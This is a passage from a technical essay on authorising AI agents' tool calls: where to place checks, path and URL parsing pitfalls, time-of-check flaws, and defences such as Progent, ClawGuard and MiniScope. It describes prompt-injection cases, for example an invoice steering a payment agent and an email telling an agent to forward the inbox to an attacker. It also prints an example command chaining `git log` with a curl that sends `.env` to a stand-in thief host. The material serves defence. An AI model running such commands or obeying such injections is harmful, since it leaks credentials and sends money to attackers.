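| Hijacked model | Needs a tool that can run code or contact the service | Limited to the grant, unless it finds a route past the gateway | Limited to the grant |
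| Compromised runtime | Switches the check off | Limited to the grant, unless it finds a route past the gateway | Limited to the grant |
| Compromised sub-agent | Switches off the check in its own process | Limited to its derived token, unless it finds a route past the gateway | Limited to its derived token |

### Inside the agent's process

In this position, the check is a function that the runtime calls just before it runs a tool. It needs no extra server or network request, and it can use information that a gateway may lack. Akto, a security vendor, points out that the application can identify the logged-in user and what that user is allowed to see.

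A hijacked model can't alter the function, because the model only produces text, but an attacker who runs code in the agent's process can delete the function. Ordinary framework behaviour can also let actions through. *Stop Means Stop* (Khan, 2026) found that approval steps in five agent frameworks allowed a parallel action to go ahead while the run was paused.

The main drawback is maintenance. A company with forty agents has forty copies of the check to keep up to date, possibly in several programming languages. Akto considers this the hardest position to manage centrally, because each team owns the code that does the checking.

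### At a gateway

A gateway is a separate server that receives tool calls, checks them and forwards the permitted ones. AWS, Amazon's cloud business, offers a gateway that checks calls against rules its customers write in Cedar. AWS announced the general release of this rule checking in March 2026 (*Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore is now generally available*).

The rules need the same care as the constraints in a token. A sample policy in AWS's *Understanding Cedar policies* is meant to let a user called John process refunds of $500 or less. It contains the condition `context.input.amount < 500`, so it refuses a refund of exactly $500. It also allows negative amounts, unless something else excludes them.

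*Mandato* (2026) describes a gateway that a company can add without modifying its agents or tools. Agents connect to the gateway as if it were the MCP server, and the gateway connects to the real servers. Those servers accept only connections that the gateway has authenticated with mutual TLS, so an agent cannot bypass the gateway. If a call needs human approval, the gateway holds it and shows the approver the call next to the relevant clause of the grant.

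Obsidian Security, which sells a competing approach, lists three drawbacks of gateways: delay, a single point of failure and the damage one fault can do. In its example, ten tool calls add a full second to a task, which implies a tenth of a second per decision. Even a fast gateway stops every agent behind it if it fails, and puts every service that trusts it at risk if an attacker takes it over.

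Some products sold as AI gateways sit between an application and its model provider. Akto warns that the agent's tool calls never pass through such a gateway. At most, the gateway receives the model's proposed call, which the runtime may change before making it.

### Inside the tool's own service

At the MCP Dev Summit 2026 in New York, Michael Schwartz, founder of the identity software company Gluu, argued for a check in every service. According to Biometric Update's *AI agent delegation via MCP has gaps a Murderbot could walk through*, he objected that relying on a gateway means trusting all the traffic beyond it. The *zero trust* approach to security is meant to avoid that assumption by having services verify requests even when they come from inside the company's network.

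Schwartz wants each service to have its own policy engine, software that evaluates authorisation rules. He calls it a "Governor Module", after the software that controls the robot in Martha Wells's *Murderbot* books. That robot hacks its own module, so the fictional version is closer to a check in the agent's process than to his proposal.

His argument is persuasive for payments. If an attacker takes over a gateway like Mandato's and invents a payment to A-22, a payment service that trusts the gateway will make the payment. A service that also verifies the payment agent's token chain and signed proof will refuse, because the gateway doesn't have the agent's key.

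The drawback is another component to install and update in each service. Schwartz notes that all these engines would produce decision logs, and that people would need more "operational leverage" to use the extra data. A company also can't install a policy engine on an outside service, such as its bank's servers, so a gateway may be the last place where it can apply its own rules. Within the company, a second check in the service makes most sense for payments, deletions and other actions that are hard to undo.

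### Storing grants in a table

Signed tokens are unnecessary if one trusted process handles every call and stores all the grants. *Causality Laundering* (2026) describes such a system, called ARM, a proxy between the model and the MCP server that keeps each grant as an ordinary read-only Python object. Code running inside the proxy could still change these objects, since Python's read-only setting is easy to bypass. The protection comes from running the proxy as a separate process whose memory the agent cannot reach. The PDP-1 at MIT protected its capability lists in much the same way.

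Keeping grants in a table has practical advantages over using tokens. An administrator can cancel a grant by deleting its row, the process can count how many payments an agent has made, and agents don't need to see what their grants contain. Mandato's gateway checks for cancelled grants and used-up quotas on every call, which an enforcement point that verifies tokens offline cannot do.

The process still has to identify which agent is calling. On a single machine, it can give each agent its own connection. Across a network, the agents need to authenticate, for instance with mutual TLS, so cryptography may be necessary even though the grants are unsigned.

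Signed grants are useful when the party that checks a call can't read the table or shouldn't depend on it. A bank can't read its customer's internal records, but if the customer's agent presents a signed token, the bank can check the grant with the issuer's public key, without asking the customer about each payment. A company with servers in several regions could use a central table, but each region would then need a connection to it for every call. Signed tokens also let an orchestrating agent create a narrower grant without permission to edit the table.

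A signature protects a grant only from alteration and forgery. Niyikiza warns that an enforcement point provides no security if it doesn't check the constraints, whatever the token's format.

### Routes around the check

A check covers only the calls that pass through it. *Complete mediation* is the principle that every access to a protected object must go through the check that governs it. *Proof-Carrying Contracts* (2026) traces the principle to a 1975 paper by Saltzer and Schroeder and points out that mediation is complete only if the agent has no way to act except through the check. A *reference monitor* is a component that mediates every access, resists tampering and is simple enough to verify.

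*Governed MCP* (2026) shows that coverage is easy to overestimate. Its author built a tool-call check into an operating system called Anima OS and at first claimed that it mediated all 123 paths from agents to the system. After a recount in July 2026 found 59 paths, 43 of them mediated, the author withdrew the claim. The check covers the MCP tools, but six paths through system calls (a program's direct requests to the operating system) remain open.

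The most obvious gap in ordinary agents comes from tools that run shell commands. Suppose the invoice agent has `run_command` as well as `send_payment`. A hijacked model could propose a command that contacts the bank directly, and the enforcement point would receive a call to `run_command` with no payee or amount to check. *Kairos* (2026) makes the general point that a monitor placed where the runtime dispatches tools can observe only the actions an agent declares.

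*Kairos* instead puts the monitor on the host machine, where it examines everything that enters or leaves the agent's isolated environment. If the monitor cannot yet determine whether an action is authorised, it can hold the action and release it later. It must also notify the agent when it refuses an action, or the agent will carry on as though the action had succeeded.

A command that reaches the bank directly still needs a credential, and GitHub's *Under the hood* (2026) explains how an agent might find one. GitHub's standard automation system keeps access tokens and keys in environment variables and configuration files that every process on the machine can read. An agent with a shell can search these, along with system files and logs, and publish what it finds in a public comment.

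GitHub's system for running agents keeps secrets out of the agent's *container*, an isolated environment for running programs. One trusted container holds the credentials for MCP servers, and another holds the key for the language model. GitHub's *Security Architecture* assumes that an attacker may fully control a container and do anything its privileges allow, so the design does not rely on the agent's software working as intended.

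Apache Magpie's *Secure agent setup* describes a simpler measure, a wrapper that removes variables such as `$GH_TOKEN` before the agent starts. The wrapper doesn't protect secrets stored in project files. Anthropic's *Securely deploying AI agents* also warns about files such as `.env`, which often contain passwords and remain readable when the folder is read-only. It recommends running a proxy outside the agent's environment to add the credential to each outgoing request, so the agent can use a service without seeing the credential.

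The proxy can check only the traffic that passes through it. Administrators often direct traffic to a proxy by setting an environment variable, but some programs ignore that variable, as the `fetch()` function in Node.js does by default. Anthropic suggests a container whose only outside network connection is a socket to the proxy, so that a program fails if it ignores the variable and tries to connect directly.

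A network proxy also can't normally read an encrypted HTTPS request, so it can limit which sites an agent contacts but can't tell a payment of 180 from one of 500. To check the arguments, the company must either let the proxy decrypt the traffic or give the agent a tool that sends the request from outside the container.

Services can block calls that bypass the check by rejecting credentials they don't recognize. In *Sovereign Execution Broker* (2026), a broker checks the calls. Every interface that can change a cloud resource accepts only the broker's credentials, so an agent that reaches one directly has no valid credential to use.

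An agent that writes software is harder to isolate because it needs compilers, scripts and much of the file system. GitHub mounts the machine's files read-only and hides selected folders behind empty ones. The agent can queue changes to GitHub but cannot make them itself. After the agent exits, separate programs check the type, number and content of the queued changes, with limits such as three pull requests per run.

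### File paths

A call that passes the check can still reach the wrong resource. The enforcement point approves a value, such as a path or a supplier's name, and the tool determines which resource that value refers to. Under Niyikiza's draft, "the tool remains responsible for resolving that invocation to the correct resource."

Tools often mishandle what the check leaves to them. *Tracing MCP Security Vulnerabilities* (2026) identified 24 confirmed vulnerabilities in MCP software. Most involved path traversal (reaching files outside the intended folder), command injection (getting a tool to run extra commands) or remote code execution.

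The draft's sample rule for file paths, which resolves any `.` and `..` before comparing, is called `path_containment`:

```json
"path": { "constraint_type": "path_containment",
          "root": "/data/public" }
```

The enforcement point also removes surplus slashes and compares the path with the root folder by folder, so its answers differ from those of a simple check on how the text begins:

| Path in the call | Text comparison | `path_containment` |
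|---|---|---|
| `/data/public/2026//report.pdf` | Passes | Passes |
| `/data/public-old/report.pdf` | Passes | Refused |
| `/data/public/../private/pay.csv` | Passes | Refused |
| `/data/./public/report.pdf` | Refused | Passes |

The rule checks only the text of the path. Suppose `/data/public/latest` is a *symbolic link*, a file that redirects to another path, in this case `/data/private/pay.csv`. The path satisfies the constraint, but a tool that follows the link will open the private file. *MCP-38* (2026), a catalogue of threats to MCP systems, lists unresolved links among the common causes of path traversal.

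A gateway can't prevent this because it can't see the links on the tool's disk, so the tool has to check when it opens the file. On Linux, it can open the permitted folder first and then use the `openat2` system call with the `RESOLVE_BENEATH` option, which fails if a link or `..` leads outside that folder. The tool should then use the file handle that the call returns, because looking up the path again could lead to a different file.

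Repeated decoding can also change a path after the check. In web addresses, `%2e` stands for a full stop. If the enforcement point receives `/data/public/%2e%2e/private`, it may treat `%2e%2e` as an ordinary folder name. A tool that later decodes the path would find `..` and leave the public folder. The path should be decoded and normalised once, before the check, and the tool should use the result without decoding it again.

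### Web addresses

Two programs can also find different destinations in the same web address:

```
https://bank.example\@thief.example/
```

Browsers treat the backslash in `https://bank.example\@thief.example` as a slash, so they connect to `bank.example`. Python's standard `urlsplit` function treats the text between `//` and `@` as login details and gives the host as `thief.example`. If the enforcement point reads addresses as a browser does and the tool uses `urlsplit`, a rule allowing only `bank.example` will let the tool contact `thief.example`.

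The safest solution is for one program to parse the address and pass the separate parts to the code that makes the connection. If the enforcement point and the tool are on different machines, the runtime should put the address in an unambiguous normal form before signing, here `https://bank.example/@thief.example/`, and the enforcement point should refuse any address that isn't in that form. If the enforcement point rewrote the address itself, the change would invalidate the agent's signed proof for any service that checks it later.

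For a short list of sites, it's easier to avoid addresses altogether. The tool could accept a value such as `site="bank"` and look up the address itself.

A permitted site can also send the tool elsewhere with a redirect, so the tool should check each new address before following it.

Network filters have a related weakness. By default, Anthropic's sandbox allows or blocks an encrypted connection based on the host name the program supplies. Because large content delivery networks serve many sites from the same machines, a program can name a permitted site when it connects, then request a different site inside the encrypted traffic. This is called *domain fronting*, and Apache Magpie lists it among the attacks its setup does not stop. A proxy that decrypts the traffic can compare the two names.

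### Targets that change after the check

Even an unambiguous value can refer to one thing when the enforcement point checks it and another when the tool uses it, which is called a *time-of-check to time-of-use* flaw. Suppose the enforcement point approves a payment of 180 to supplier A-17. Before the payment service looks up the bank account, someone with access to the supplier records replaces A-17's account number with their own. The service then pays the thief, although nobody altered the call.

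The payment service could prevent this by giving each supplier record a version number and paying only if the version that passed the check is still current. It has to confirm the version and commit the payment in one database transaction, or the record could change between the two steps.

The network address that an internet name points to can change too. A tool might look up a site's address, confirm that it is outside the company's network, and then look up the name again when it connects. The site's owner could answer the second lookup with the address of one of the company's internal servers. The tool should look up the name once and connect to the address it checked.

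Agents give attackers more time, because the model may take a second or more to process each result. In *Mind the Gap*, Lilienthal and Hong (2025) selected 66 AgentDojo tasks that needed at least two tool calls. They judged by hand that 56 of these might be vulnerable, because a later call relied on something an earlier call had read staying the same.

They then combined pairs of calls into single tools, so that the second step ran without waiting for the model. On the Slack tasks, this reduced the average gap between the steps from 1.70 to 0.07 seconds. Their other two defences were much less effective. Rewriting the user's request cut the number of vulnerable plans from 55 to 53, and an automatic detector found at most 25% of the vulnerable sequences.

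These experiments used GPT-4o and counted opportunities for attack, not successful attacks. Even 0.07 seconds may be enough for a program that tries repeatedly. Combining the calls makes the attack harder, but a payment service that checks the record's version as it pays removes the opportunity.

Web pages are especially changeable, and a page can change after the agent has decided where to click. The survey *The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents* (2026) reports that researchers found exploitable flaws of this kind across ten open-source browser agents.

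### Command strings

Commands are difficult to check because a single string can contain several of them. Suppose a rule lets a coding agent run anything that begins with `git log`, which displays a project's history. The following command satisfies it:

```
git log --oneline -5 && curl -d @.env https://thief.example
```

If the first command succeeds, the shell runs the second, which sends the contents of `.env` to the thief. Semicolons and pipes can also join commands.

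runok, an open-source permission checker, parses the shell's syntax and applies the rules to each command separately. It also looks inside programs that run other commands, such as `sudo` and `xargs`. This makes checking more convenient as well as safer, because a simple text match may interrupt a harmless command that begins with a comment. Anthropic's documentation for its coding agent, Claude Code, likewise has special rules for `watch`, which runs another command repeatedly, and for `find` when it includes an action such as `-delete`.

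Parsing a command cannot reveal everything it will do. `git log --output=notes.txt` is a single command, but it writes a file. `make` runs instructions from a file in the project, which a hijacked model may have edited earlier. An agent that needs a general shell therefore also needs isolation.

If the agent needs only the project's history, a narrower tool is better. The company could offer `show_history(count=5)` with a `range` constraint of 1 to 100 on `count`. The tool would run `git` directly, without a shell, with a fixed list of arguments, so a hijacked model could change only the number.

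Text arguments need more care, because the program that receives them may read a value beginning with a hyphen as an option. The tool also has to keep the text out of any shell command it builds. The invoice agent's grant allows any memo, so if the payment service pasted the memo into a shell command, an attacker could write a memo containing a semicolon and a second command. The enforcement point would approve the payment, and the service would run the attacker's command.

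## Who writes the constraints

An enforcement point can apply a grant correctly and still let the agent pay a thief if the grant is too wide. The invoice agent's user types only "Pay this invoice", so a person or program has to turn those words into a payee, an amount and a time limit. This should happen before the agent opens the file, because after that the attacker's text can influence those limits. But the payee and the amount often appear only in the invoice.

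Constraints come from four main sources, which a deployment can combine:

| Source | What goes in | What comes out | How it fails |
|---|---|---|---|
| Developer's template | Tool descriptions and the tasks the developer expects | A reusable grant with blanks to fill in | Nobody wrote one for this task |
| Organisation's rules | Job roles, spending limits, forbidden actions | Limits that apply to every task | They leave too much room within a single task |
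| Language model | The user's request and the list of tools | A policy for this task | The model misreads the request or allows too much |
| User's confirmation | A proposed permission or call | Approval or refusal | The user approves without reading |

### Templates and company rules

A developer's template for paying invoices might allow only `send_payment`, cap the amount at 500 and expire after five minutes. If the user picks the supplier from a menu, ordinary code can copy the choice into the grant, so text in the invoice cannot change it.

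Templates take work to write, and each covers only the tasks its developer foresaw. *Agent-Sentry* (2026) tested a rival system on new agents for GitHub, shopping and daily life, but had to add three handwritten policies because the system's released ones did not cover those agents. Using one template for many tasks saves effort but restricts the agent less. For example, a template for "handle my email" has to allow sending, even when the user only asks for a summary of unread messages.

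An organisation's rules apply whatever the task. In *Dynamic Capability Scoping for Enterprise AI Agents*, Noyan proposes a ceiling on permissions for each job role, a classifier that narrows those permissions to suit the current task, and a ban on certain combinations. A company might let an agent read payroll files or send external email, but not both. If the classifier misjudges the task, the ceiling and the bans still hold. However, the ceiling for an accounts department has to include every supplier the department pays, so it won't stop a hijacked model from paying the wrong supplier.

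### Policies written by a model

Progent, a system developed mainly at UC Berkeley, uses a language model to write a policy for each request. Shi, He and colleagues (2025), in *Progent*, define a policy as a list of rules. Each rule allows or forbids one tool under conditions on its arguments. In their notation, a rule for the invoice agent could be:

```
allow send_payment
  when { payee == "A-17", 0 < amount and amount <= 180 },
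  fallback return "Payment not allowed"
```

Conditions can compare values, test whether a value is on a list, measure an array or match a text pattern. Progent applies `forbid` rules before `allow` rules and blocks any call that no rule allows. After a block, the fallback can end the task, ask the user or, by default, return an error so that the agent tries something else. The conditions cover only a call's arguments, so a time limit would have to come from elsewhere, such as a token's expiry date.

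Text patterns need particular care. Progent stores its rules as JSON Schema, where a pattern can match any part of the text unless its author anchors it to the start and end. If a model wrote the pattern `@example\.com` to keep email inside a company, the rule would also allow `eve@example.com.thief.net`.

The policy can change as the agent works:

1. Before the agent starts, a model reads the user's request and the tool descriptions and writes the initial policy.
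2. After each tool call, a model decides whether the policy may need to change. It sees the request and the call, but not the tool's result.
3. If a change may be needed, a model reads the result and proposes a new policy.
4. The solver Z3 checks whether the new policy allows any call that the old one did not.
5. If it allows none, Progent applies the new policy automatically. Otherwise the change is an *expansion* and needs approval.

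Automatic changes must therefore meet the condition for derived tokens, C(child) ⊆ C(parent), with the old policy as the parent and the new one as the child. A policy that drops A-22 and adds X-99 fails this condition, even though the number of payees stays the same. Between approvals, the agent's authority can shrink but never grow, a property Shi and colleagues call *monotonic confinement*.

In one example, a user asks an agent to do the tasks in an email from Alice. The initial policy allows only a search for that email. In it, Alice asks for a summary of recent emails to be posted to Slack, so the model proposes adding tools to read mail and post to Slack, which is an expansion. Once the agent has looked up the user's Slack name, the model proposes limiting posts to that name, and Progent applies the change automatically. One of the recent emails contains an injection instructing the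 agent to forward the inbox to `eve@evil.com`. Even if the model follows the injection and proposes allowing `send_email`, Z3 will classify the change as an expansion.

As with derived tokens, narrowing a policy can do harm. If a policy allows payments to anyone, an invoice containing injected instructions could cause the model to restrict payments to X-99 alone.

The quality of the initial policy also depends on the request. Shi and colleagues assume that the request is harmless, but users paste text from emails and web pages into their prompts, and that text may contain an injection. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* warns that an ambiguous or manipulated request can produce a broader grant than the user intended. A coding-agent design in *Authority Is Not a String* (2026) limits this risk by having the model predict the grant before it sees any repository text or tool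 output. The host program turns the prediction into a limit on authority for the whole task, and sub-agents can only receive authority within that limit.

### Tests of Progent

Shi and colleagues tested Progent on AgentDojo and on ASB, a benchmark with ten agent scenarios and five attack templates. The agents ran on GPT-4o, which also wrote the policies. On AgentDojo, the researchers gave every agent a fixed rule allowing harmless read-only tools, in addition to these policies. They left out two travel attacks that only steer the agent towards a particular hotel, and corrected the scoring of a Slack attack that AgentDojo counted as successful even when Progent had blocked the call.

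The attack success rate fell from 70.3% to 3.9% on ASB. Most of the remaining failures involved attack tools whose names and descriptions closely resembled those of legitimate tools, and policies written by hand eliminated them. On AgentDojo, the result depended on how Progent handled changes to the policy:

| Handling of policy changes | Attack success rate on AgentDojo |
|---|---|
| No defence | 39.9% |
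| Initial policy only, never changed | 2.5% |
| Every change accepted | 1.0% |
| Narrowing accepted, expansions refused | Slightly below 1.0% |
| A careful person reviews the initial policy and each expansion | 0% |

The team's headline figure of 1.0% comes from the setting that accepts every change. Z3's verdict blocks nothing there, so the low rate reflects how well GPT-4o wrote the policies, not the guarantee of monotonic confinement. The 0% figure is less informative than it looks, because the team assumed a reviewer who never grants unrestricted access to `send_money` and always rejects a malicious address.

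Progent first appeared in April 2025, and these figures come from its May 2026 revision, though the models are older. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) criticized an earlier version because a malicious tool result might lead the policy writer to relax its own constraints. The check for expansions addresses this, provided that the approver rejects any expansion caused by such a result.

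Outside tests generally show that Progent blocks most of AgentDojo's attacks. Narisetty, Kore and colleagues (2026) found in *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* that Progent also protected a small open model, including against one attack they designed specifically to target Progent. *SecureClaw* (2026), which presents a competing system, reran Progent on all 629 AgentDojo cases and counted 24 successful attacks, or 3.8%. The 629 cases include the hotel attacks that Shi and colleagues excluded, which may account for some of the difference from their results.

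### Rules the user confirms in advance

*ClawGuard* (Zhao, Li and colleagues, 2026) describes a system that combines three of the four sources. An operator first sets base rules that nothing can override, such as a ban on reading stored passwords. Before the agent calls any tool, a model turns the user's request into task rules, which the user can edit and must confirm. If the user asks the agent to summarise some blog posts and save the result, the task rules allow access to the blog's address and the reports folder, and forbid shell commands.

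ClawGuard then blocks a call if anything it checks is on a deny list, runs the call if everything it checks is on an allow list, and asks the user about the rest. If the user doesn't answer in time, ClawGuard blocks the call.

ClawGuard's task rules cover commands, file paths and network addresses, which suits a coding or browsing agent. They suit the invoice agent less well because, as published, they have no category for a payee or an amount. A rule allowing `send_payment` and the bank's address would therefore treat payments to A-17 and X-99 alike.

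The tests used five models, including GPT-5.4 and Claude Sonnet 4.6. The older benchmarks, AgentDojo and InjecAgent, are no longer difficult for these models. Without any added defence, GPT-5.4 and Claude Sonnet 4.6 resisted every attack adapted from them, and the other three models resisted at least 95%. Zhao and colleagues claim that ClawGuard raised the rate to 100% for all five models, but their results table gives 99.08% and 99.82% for two models on InjecAgent.

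Attacks hidden in tool descriptions and in skill files were much more successful:

| Benchmark | Where the attack comes from | Attacks prevented without ClawGuard | With ClawGuard |
|---|---|---|---|
| SkillInject | Skill files | 56.7% | 86.7% |
| MCPTox | MCP tools | 62.1% | 89.5% |
| MCPSecurityBench | MCP tools | 75.9% | 94.2% |

These are averages over the five models, with GPT-5.4 judging whether each attack had succeeded. In the security tests, ClawGuard automatically refused every call that would have needed the user's approval. With the same setting, the agents kept 87.4% of their original performance on ordinary tasks. Allowing up to three approvals per task raised this to 95.1%, but the team did not repeat the security tests with approvals allowed, so the security results apply only to the stricter setting.

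The quality of the rules seems to depend on the model that writes them. In the strict setting, GPT-5.4 lost 8.1% of its performance and DeepSeek-V3.2 lost 21.6%. Zhao and colleagues think stronger models write more precise rules.

### A payee found only in the invoice

Suppose the company has bought something from a new supplier, B-31, whose account number appears only in the invoice. An attacker may have altered the invoice to show X-99 instead. The rule for `payee` determines what happens:

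| Rule for `payee` | Honest invoice from B-31 | Altered invoice with X-99 |
|---|---|---|
| A-17 or A-22 only | Refused | Refused |
| Any payee | Paid | Paid |
| Ask about a new payee | Paid if the approver agrees | Paid if the approver agrees |

A strict list fixed in advance blocks a payment the user wanted, and a loose rule lets the thief receive the money. Progent's policy updates delay the choice between the two but don't remove it. After reading the invoice, the model may propose adding B-31 or X-99 to the policy. Z3 will report an expansion in both cases, because it compares sets of permitted calls without any information about who is owed money.

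Benchmark results show the same trade-off. CaMeL, a stricter system, fixes the plan from the user's request so that outside data cannot change it. In the *SecureClaw* comparison, no attack on CaMeL succeeded, but it completed only 29 of 97 ordinary tasks, while Progent completed 59. The gap matters more when tasks depend on what the agent discovers along the way, as in the AgentDyn benchmark. *DRIFT* (2025), which presents another competing defence, reports that every defence did poorly on that benchmark and that CaMeL completed no tasks. The benchmark's own paper, *AgentDyn* (2026), reports that agents often stopped to ask for confirmation and so finished fewer tasks.

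For payments, a company can often avoid the dilemma by using a record it already trusts. If an employee entered B-31 in a purchase order when placing it, the user can give the order number and ordinary code can copy the payee and amount into the grant. The invoice then only has to match the grant. This makes the purchase records a target for attackers, and it doesn't help with tasks that have no such record.

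### Asking for the smallest permission

*MiniScope* (Zhu, Tseng and colleagues, 2025) relies on the user but tries to ask for as little as possible. It starts from the OAuth scopes that services such as Gmail already publish. Each scope permits a set of operations, called methods. If scope A permits everything scope B permits and more, MiniScope places A above B in a hierarchy.

The agent submits a plan listing the calls it wants to make. MiniScope has to choose scopes that cover the whole plan, which is harder than it sounds because 24 of Google Calendar's 37 methods are available through more than one branch of the hierarchy. It treats the choice as an optimisation problem, where x(v) is 1 if it selects scope v and 0 if not:

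```
minimise    sum of cost(v) × x(v) over all scopes v
subject to  every planned call has at least one selected scope that permits it
```

The solver gives each scope a weight based on how many methods it permits. It minimizes the total weight exactly, but the choice of weight is debatable. Suppose a plan needs methods 3 and 4. Scope A permits methods 1, 2 and 3, scope B permits 1, 2 and 4, and scope C permits 3 to 7. If the weight is simply the number of methods, A and B together have a weight of 6 and C has a weight of 5, so the solver picks C. But the sum counts methods 1 and 2 twice, so A and B together expose only four methods, while C exposes five. Two choices can also tie, and *Incomparable Minima in Agent Tool Authorization* (2026) points out that MiniScope's paper does not discuss whether the best answer is unique.

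The user can refuse the chosen scopes or allow them once, for the session, or always. MiniScope keeps the real credentials away from the agent and checks every call against the granted scopes. If an email contains an instruction to delete messages and the agent adds this to its plan, the user sees a request for a wider permission and can refuse it.

Zhu and colleagues also asked five language models to choose scopes for the same plans. Commercial models matched MiniScope's answer in 70–83% of cases and open models in 20–34%. Because MiniScope's answer was the standard, the comparison can't show whether it chooses scopes better than the models do, but the models did often request more than the plan needed. The team found the same problem in real products, such as ChatGPT's Gmail connector, which requested permissions covering 50 methods when its advertised functions needed 32.

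MiniScope added only 1–6% to running time. Its main limitation is that it checks scopes but not arguments, so an agent allowed to send one email can send any email to anyone. Scopes may be too broad even for ordinary apps. *OAuthHub* (2026) found that Google's scopes lack detail, so apps have to fetch more data than they need and filter it afterwards. Zhu and colleagues suggest extending MiniScope to limit permissions to particular recipients, but they chose broad permissions because they feared detailed questions would overwhelm users.

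### Signing approval for one call

A company can keep its list of suppliers strict and have a person approve each exception. The approval should be a signed document, so that the payment service can check it without trusting the agent's account of what the person agreed to. For B-31's invoice, it might contain:

```json
{
  "approval_id": "appr-88c2",
  "approver": "maria@example.com",
  "agent_key": "rAl9...",
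  "audience": "https://pay.example.com",
  "tool": "send_payment",
  "arguments": { "payee": "B-31", "amount": 180,
                 "memo": "Invoice 2207" },
  "payee_record_version": 6,
  "issued": 1791367500,
  "expires": 1791367620
}
```

The signature has to cover all of these fields. If it left out the arguments, a hijacked model could get approval for 180 and then send 500. The agent's key and the audience tie the approval to one agent and one service.

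The remaining fields let the payment service refuse a stale approval. Maria's approval expires after two minutes, and its identifier works only once, so it cannot authorise a second payment. If somebody replaces B-31's bank details after Maria approves, the record version becomes 7 and the service must ask her again.

If the agent's runtime draws the approval screen, an attacker who controls the runtime can show Maria one payment and have her sign another. A separate trusted program should build the screen from the fields she will sign, and show the supplier's name and bank account as well as the code B-31. It should clearly label any explanation from the model as the model's, because a hijacked model can write a convincing reason for paying X-99.

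Biometric Update's *Hypr and Proof bring human authorization controls to AI agent workflows* describes two recent products that work roughly along these lines. Hypr's AgentPass sends sensitive operations to a human supervisor, who approves them with a passkey, a private key that the owner unlocks with a fingerprint, face or PIN. In Proof's x401 system, the agent shows the user the requested action, and a hardware-protected key signs evidence linking the user's verified identity to the approved terms. The receiving service can check that evidence itself. These are product announcements, so they illustrate the mechanism but are not evidence that it prevents attacks.

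Passkeys were designed for logging in and normally sign a random challenge from a website, so a passkey signature does not automatically cover the details of a payment. To tie the signature to one payment, the service can compute the challenge from a hash of the approval document and a fresh random value.

### Approving without reading

None of this helps if Maria approves every request. People who see many harmless requests stop examining them, which security researchers call *approval fatigue*. The Progent, ClawGuard and MiniScope papers all discuss the burden on users, but none measured how often real people approve a harmful request.

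MiniScope came closest to measuring the burden, by simulating three months of Gmail use. Its simulated users ranged from one who always chose "Always allow" to one who approved each permission only once, and one was a language model told to be careful about security. Depending on the user, MiniScope asked for confirmation on 18–60% of roughly 500 requests, or one to three times a day. The language model answered a quarter as many questions as it did when every method needed its own permission.

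Users may give each question more attention when there are fewer of them, but the simulation can't show this. The options can also make a careless answer more harmful. A user who picks "Always allow" to stop the interruptions gives the agent that scope in every future session until somebody revokes it.

Progent requests approval only for policy changes that expand the agent's permissions. These made up 6% of all policy changes on AgentDojo. That low share is encouraging, but it doesn't show how many requests each task needs, and tasks in which the agent has to discover what to do would probably need more.

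Shi and colleagues also modelled a user who approves every expansion, and directly attacked the model that writes the policy. They tried an injection with instructions to allow all tools, another with instructions to permit whatever the attack needed, and an automated search for further wordings. The attack success rate rose only slightly. This suggests that a careless approver need not be disastrous if the model resists the injection, but the user's approval then adds no protection.

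## Checking where an argument's value came from

Suppose the user asks the invoice agent to pay A-17's latest invoice, which is for 240. Hidden text in the invoice claims that A-17 now collects its payments through A-22, and the model proposes this call:

```
send_payment(payee="A-22", amount=240, memo="Invoice 1043")
```

The grant permits A-22, because the company buys from that supplier too. The amount and the memo also satisfy their constraints and the runtime signs the call, so the enforcement point lets the payment through. A token limited to A-17 would have prevented the payment, but only if someone had issued it before the model read the invoice.

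*Provenance* is a record of which source an argument's value came from, such as the user's request or a retrieved document. The value "A-22" is valid, but the agent took it from the invoice when only the user should have chosen the payee, so a provenance check refuses the call.

### From a source to a tool call

Before the model reads anything, ordinary code labels each source. The user's request is trusted, and an invoice is untrusted because an outsider wrote it. The label depends on who could have written the text, so nobody has to judge whether the text looks malicious. One tool result may need several labels. In a bank statement, for example, the bank fills in the dates and amounts, but the sender of each payment writes its description, which could contain a prompt injection.

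The labels then have to follow the data. A value made from several sources gets the label of the least trusted one, so a summary that draws on both the request and the invoice is untrusted. If the agent saves that summary in a file and reads it back later, the summary must still have its label.

Before the tool runs, the enforcement point compares the source of each argument with a rule for that argument:

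| Argument | Value | Source | Rule | Result |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| `payee` | "A-22" | Invoice | Must come from the user's request | Refused |
| `amount` | 240 | Invoice | Any source, up to 500 | Passes |
| `memo` | "Invoice 1043" | Invoice | Any source | Passes |

Filling in the "Source" column is the difficult part. In an ordinary program, each instruction specifies its inputs, so other software can follow a value from step to step. A language model reads all its input together and writes new text, so the runtime cannot determine which part of the input produced "A-22". Some systems search the earlier texts for the same value. Others treat the model's output as affected by everything it has read, or keep untrusted text away from the model.

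### AgentCap's tokens and issuance checks

*AgentCap* describes a system that searches for matching values. For each call the model proposes, a policy engine decides whether to issue a token, and a gateway verifies the token before forwarding the call to an MCP server. The developer writes the policy in advance. A rule for the invoice agent could look like this:

```
grant send_payment {
  action: write
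  resource: "company_account/payments"
  intent: [pay_invoice]
  trust: >= 0.8
  requires: [read_invoice]
  ttl: 60s
  budget: 1
  bound_params: [payee]
}
```

The token lasts 60 seconds and works for one call. `bound_params` lists the arguments that need trusted support. The policy engine issues a token only if seven conditions hold:

1. AgentCap has not suspended the agent for suspicious behaviour.
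2. The tool is in the policy's catalogue.
3. The arguments in `bound_params` have acceptable provenance.
4. The policy permits the purpose that the model states for the call.
5. The agent's trust score is high enough.
6. The agent already holds valid tokens for the prerequisites, here `read_invoice`, in the same session.
7. The new token would not complete a forbidden combination, such as reading customer records and sending external messages.

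The token names the agent, session, action, resource and stated purpose. It also contains its own identifier, the issue and expiry times, the number of calls allowed, the trust score, the prerequisites, the forbidden combinations and a reference to the audit record. The policy engine signs all this with Ed25519.

The published list of fields includes neither a public key for the agent nor the arguments of the call. The gateway checks the agent's identity, the action and the resource, but the design relies on the wrapper and the network connection to deliver the payee that the policy engine approved. The signed proof in Niyikiza's draft would reveal a change of payee at that stage.

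The trust score starts at 0.8. Each normal outcome raises it by 1% of its distance from 1, and each anomaly, including a refused request, cuts it by 30%. An agent loses write access after two anomalies and is suspended after three. The sample banking policy requires a score of 0.8 to send money. A single refusal at the start would therefore lower the score to 0.56 and stop the agent from making payments until it had recorded 79 normal outcomes. This would contain an attack quickly, but it would also block payments after an honest mistake.

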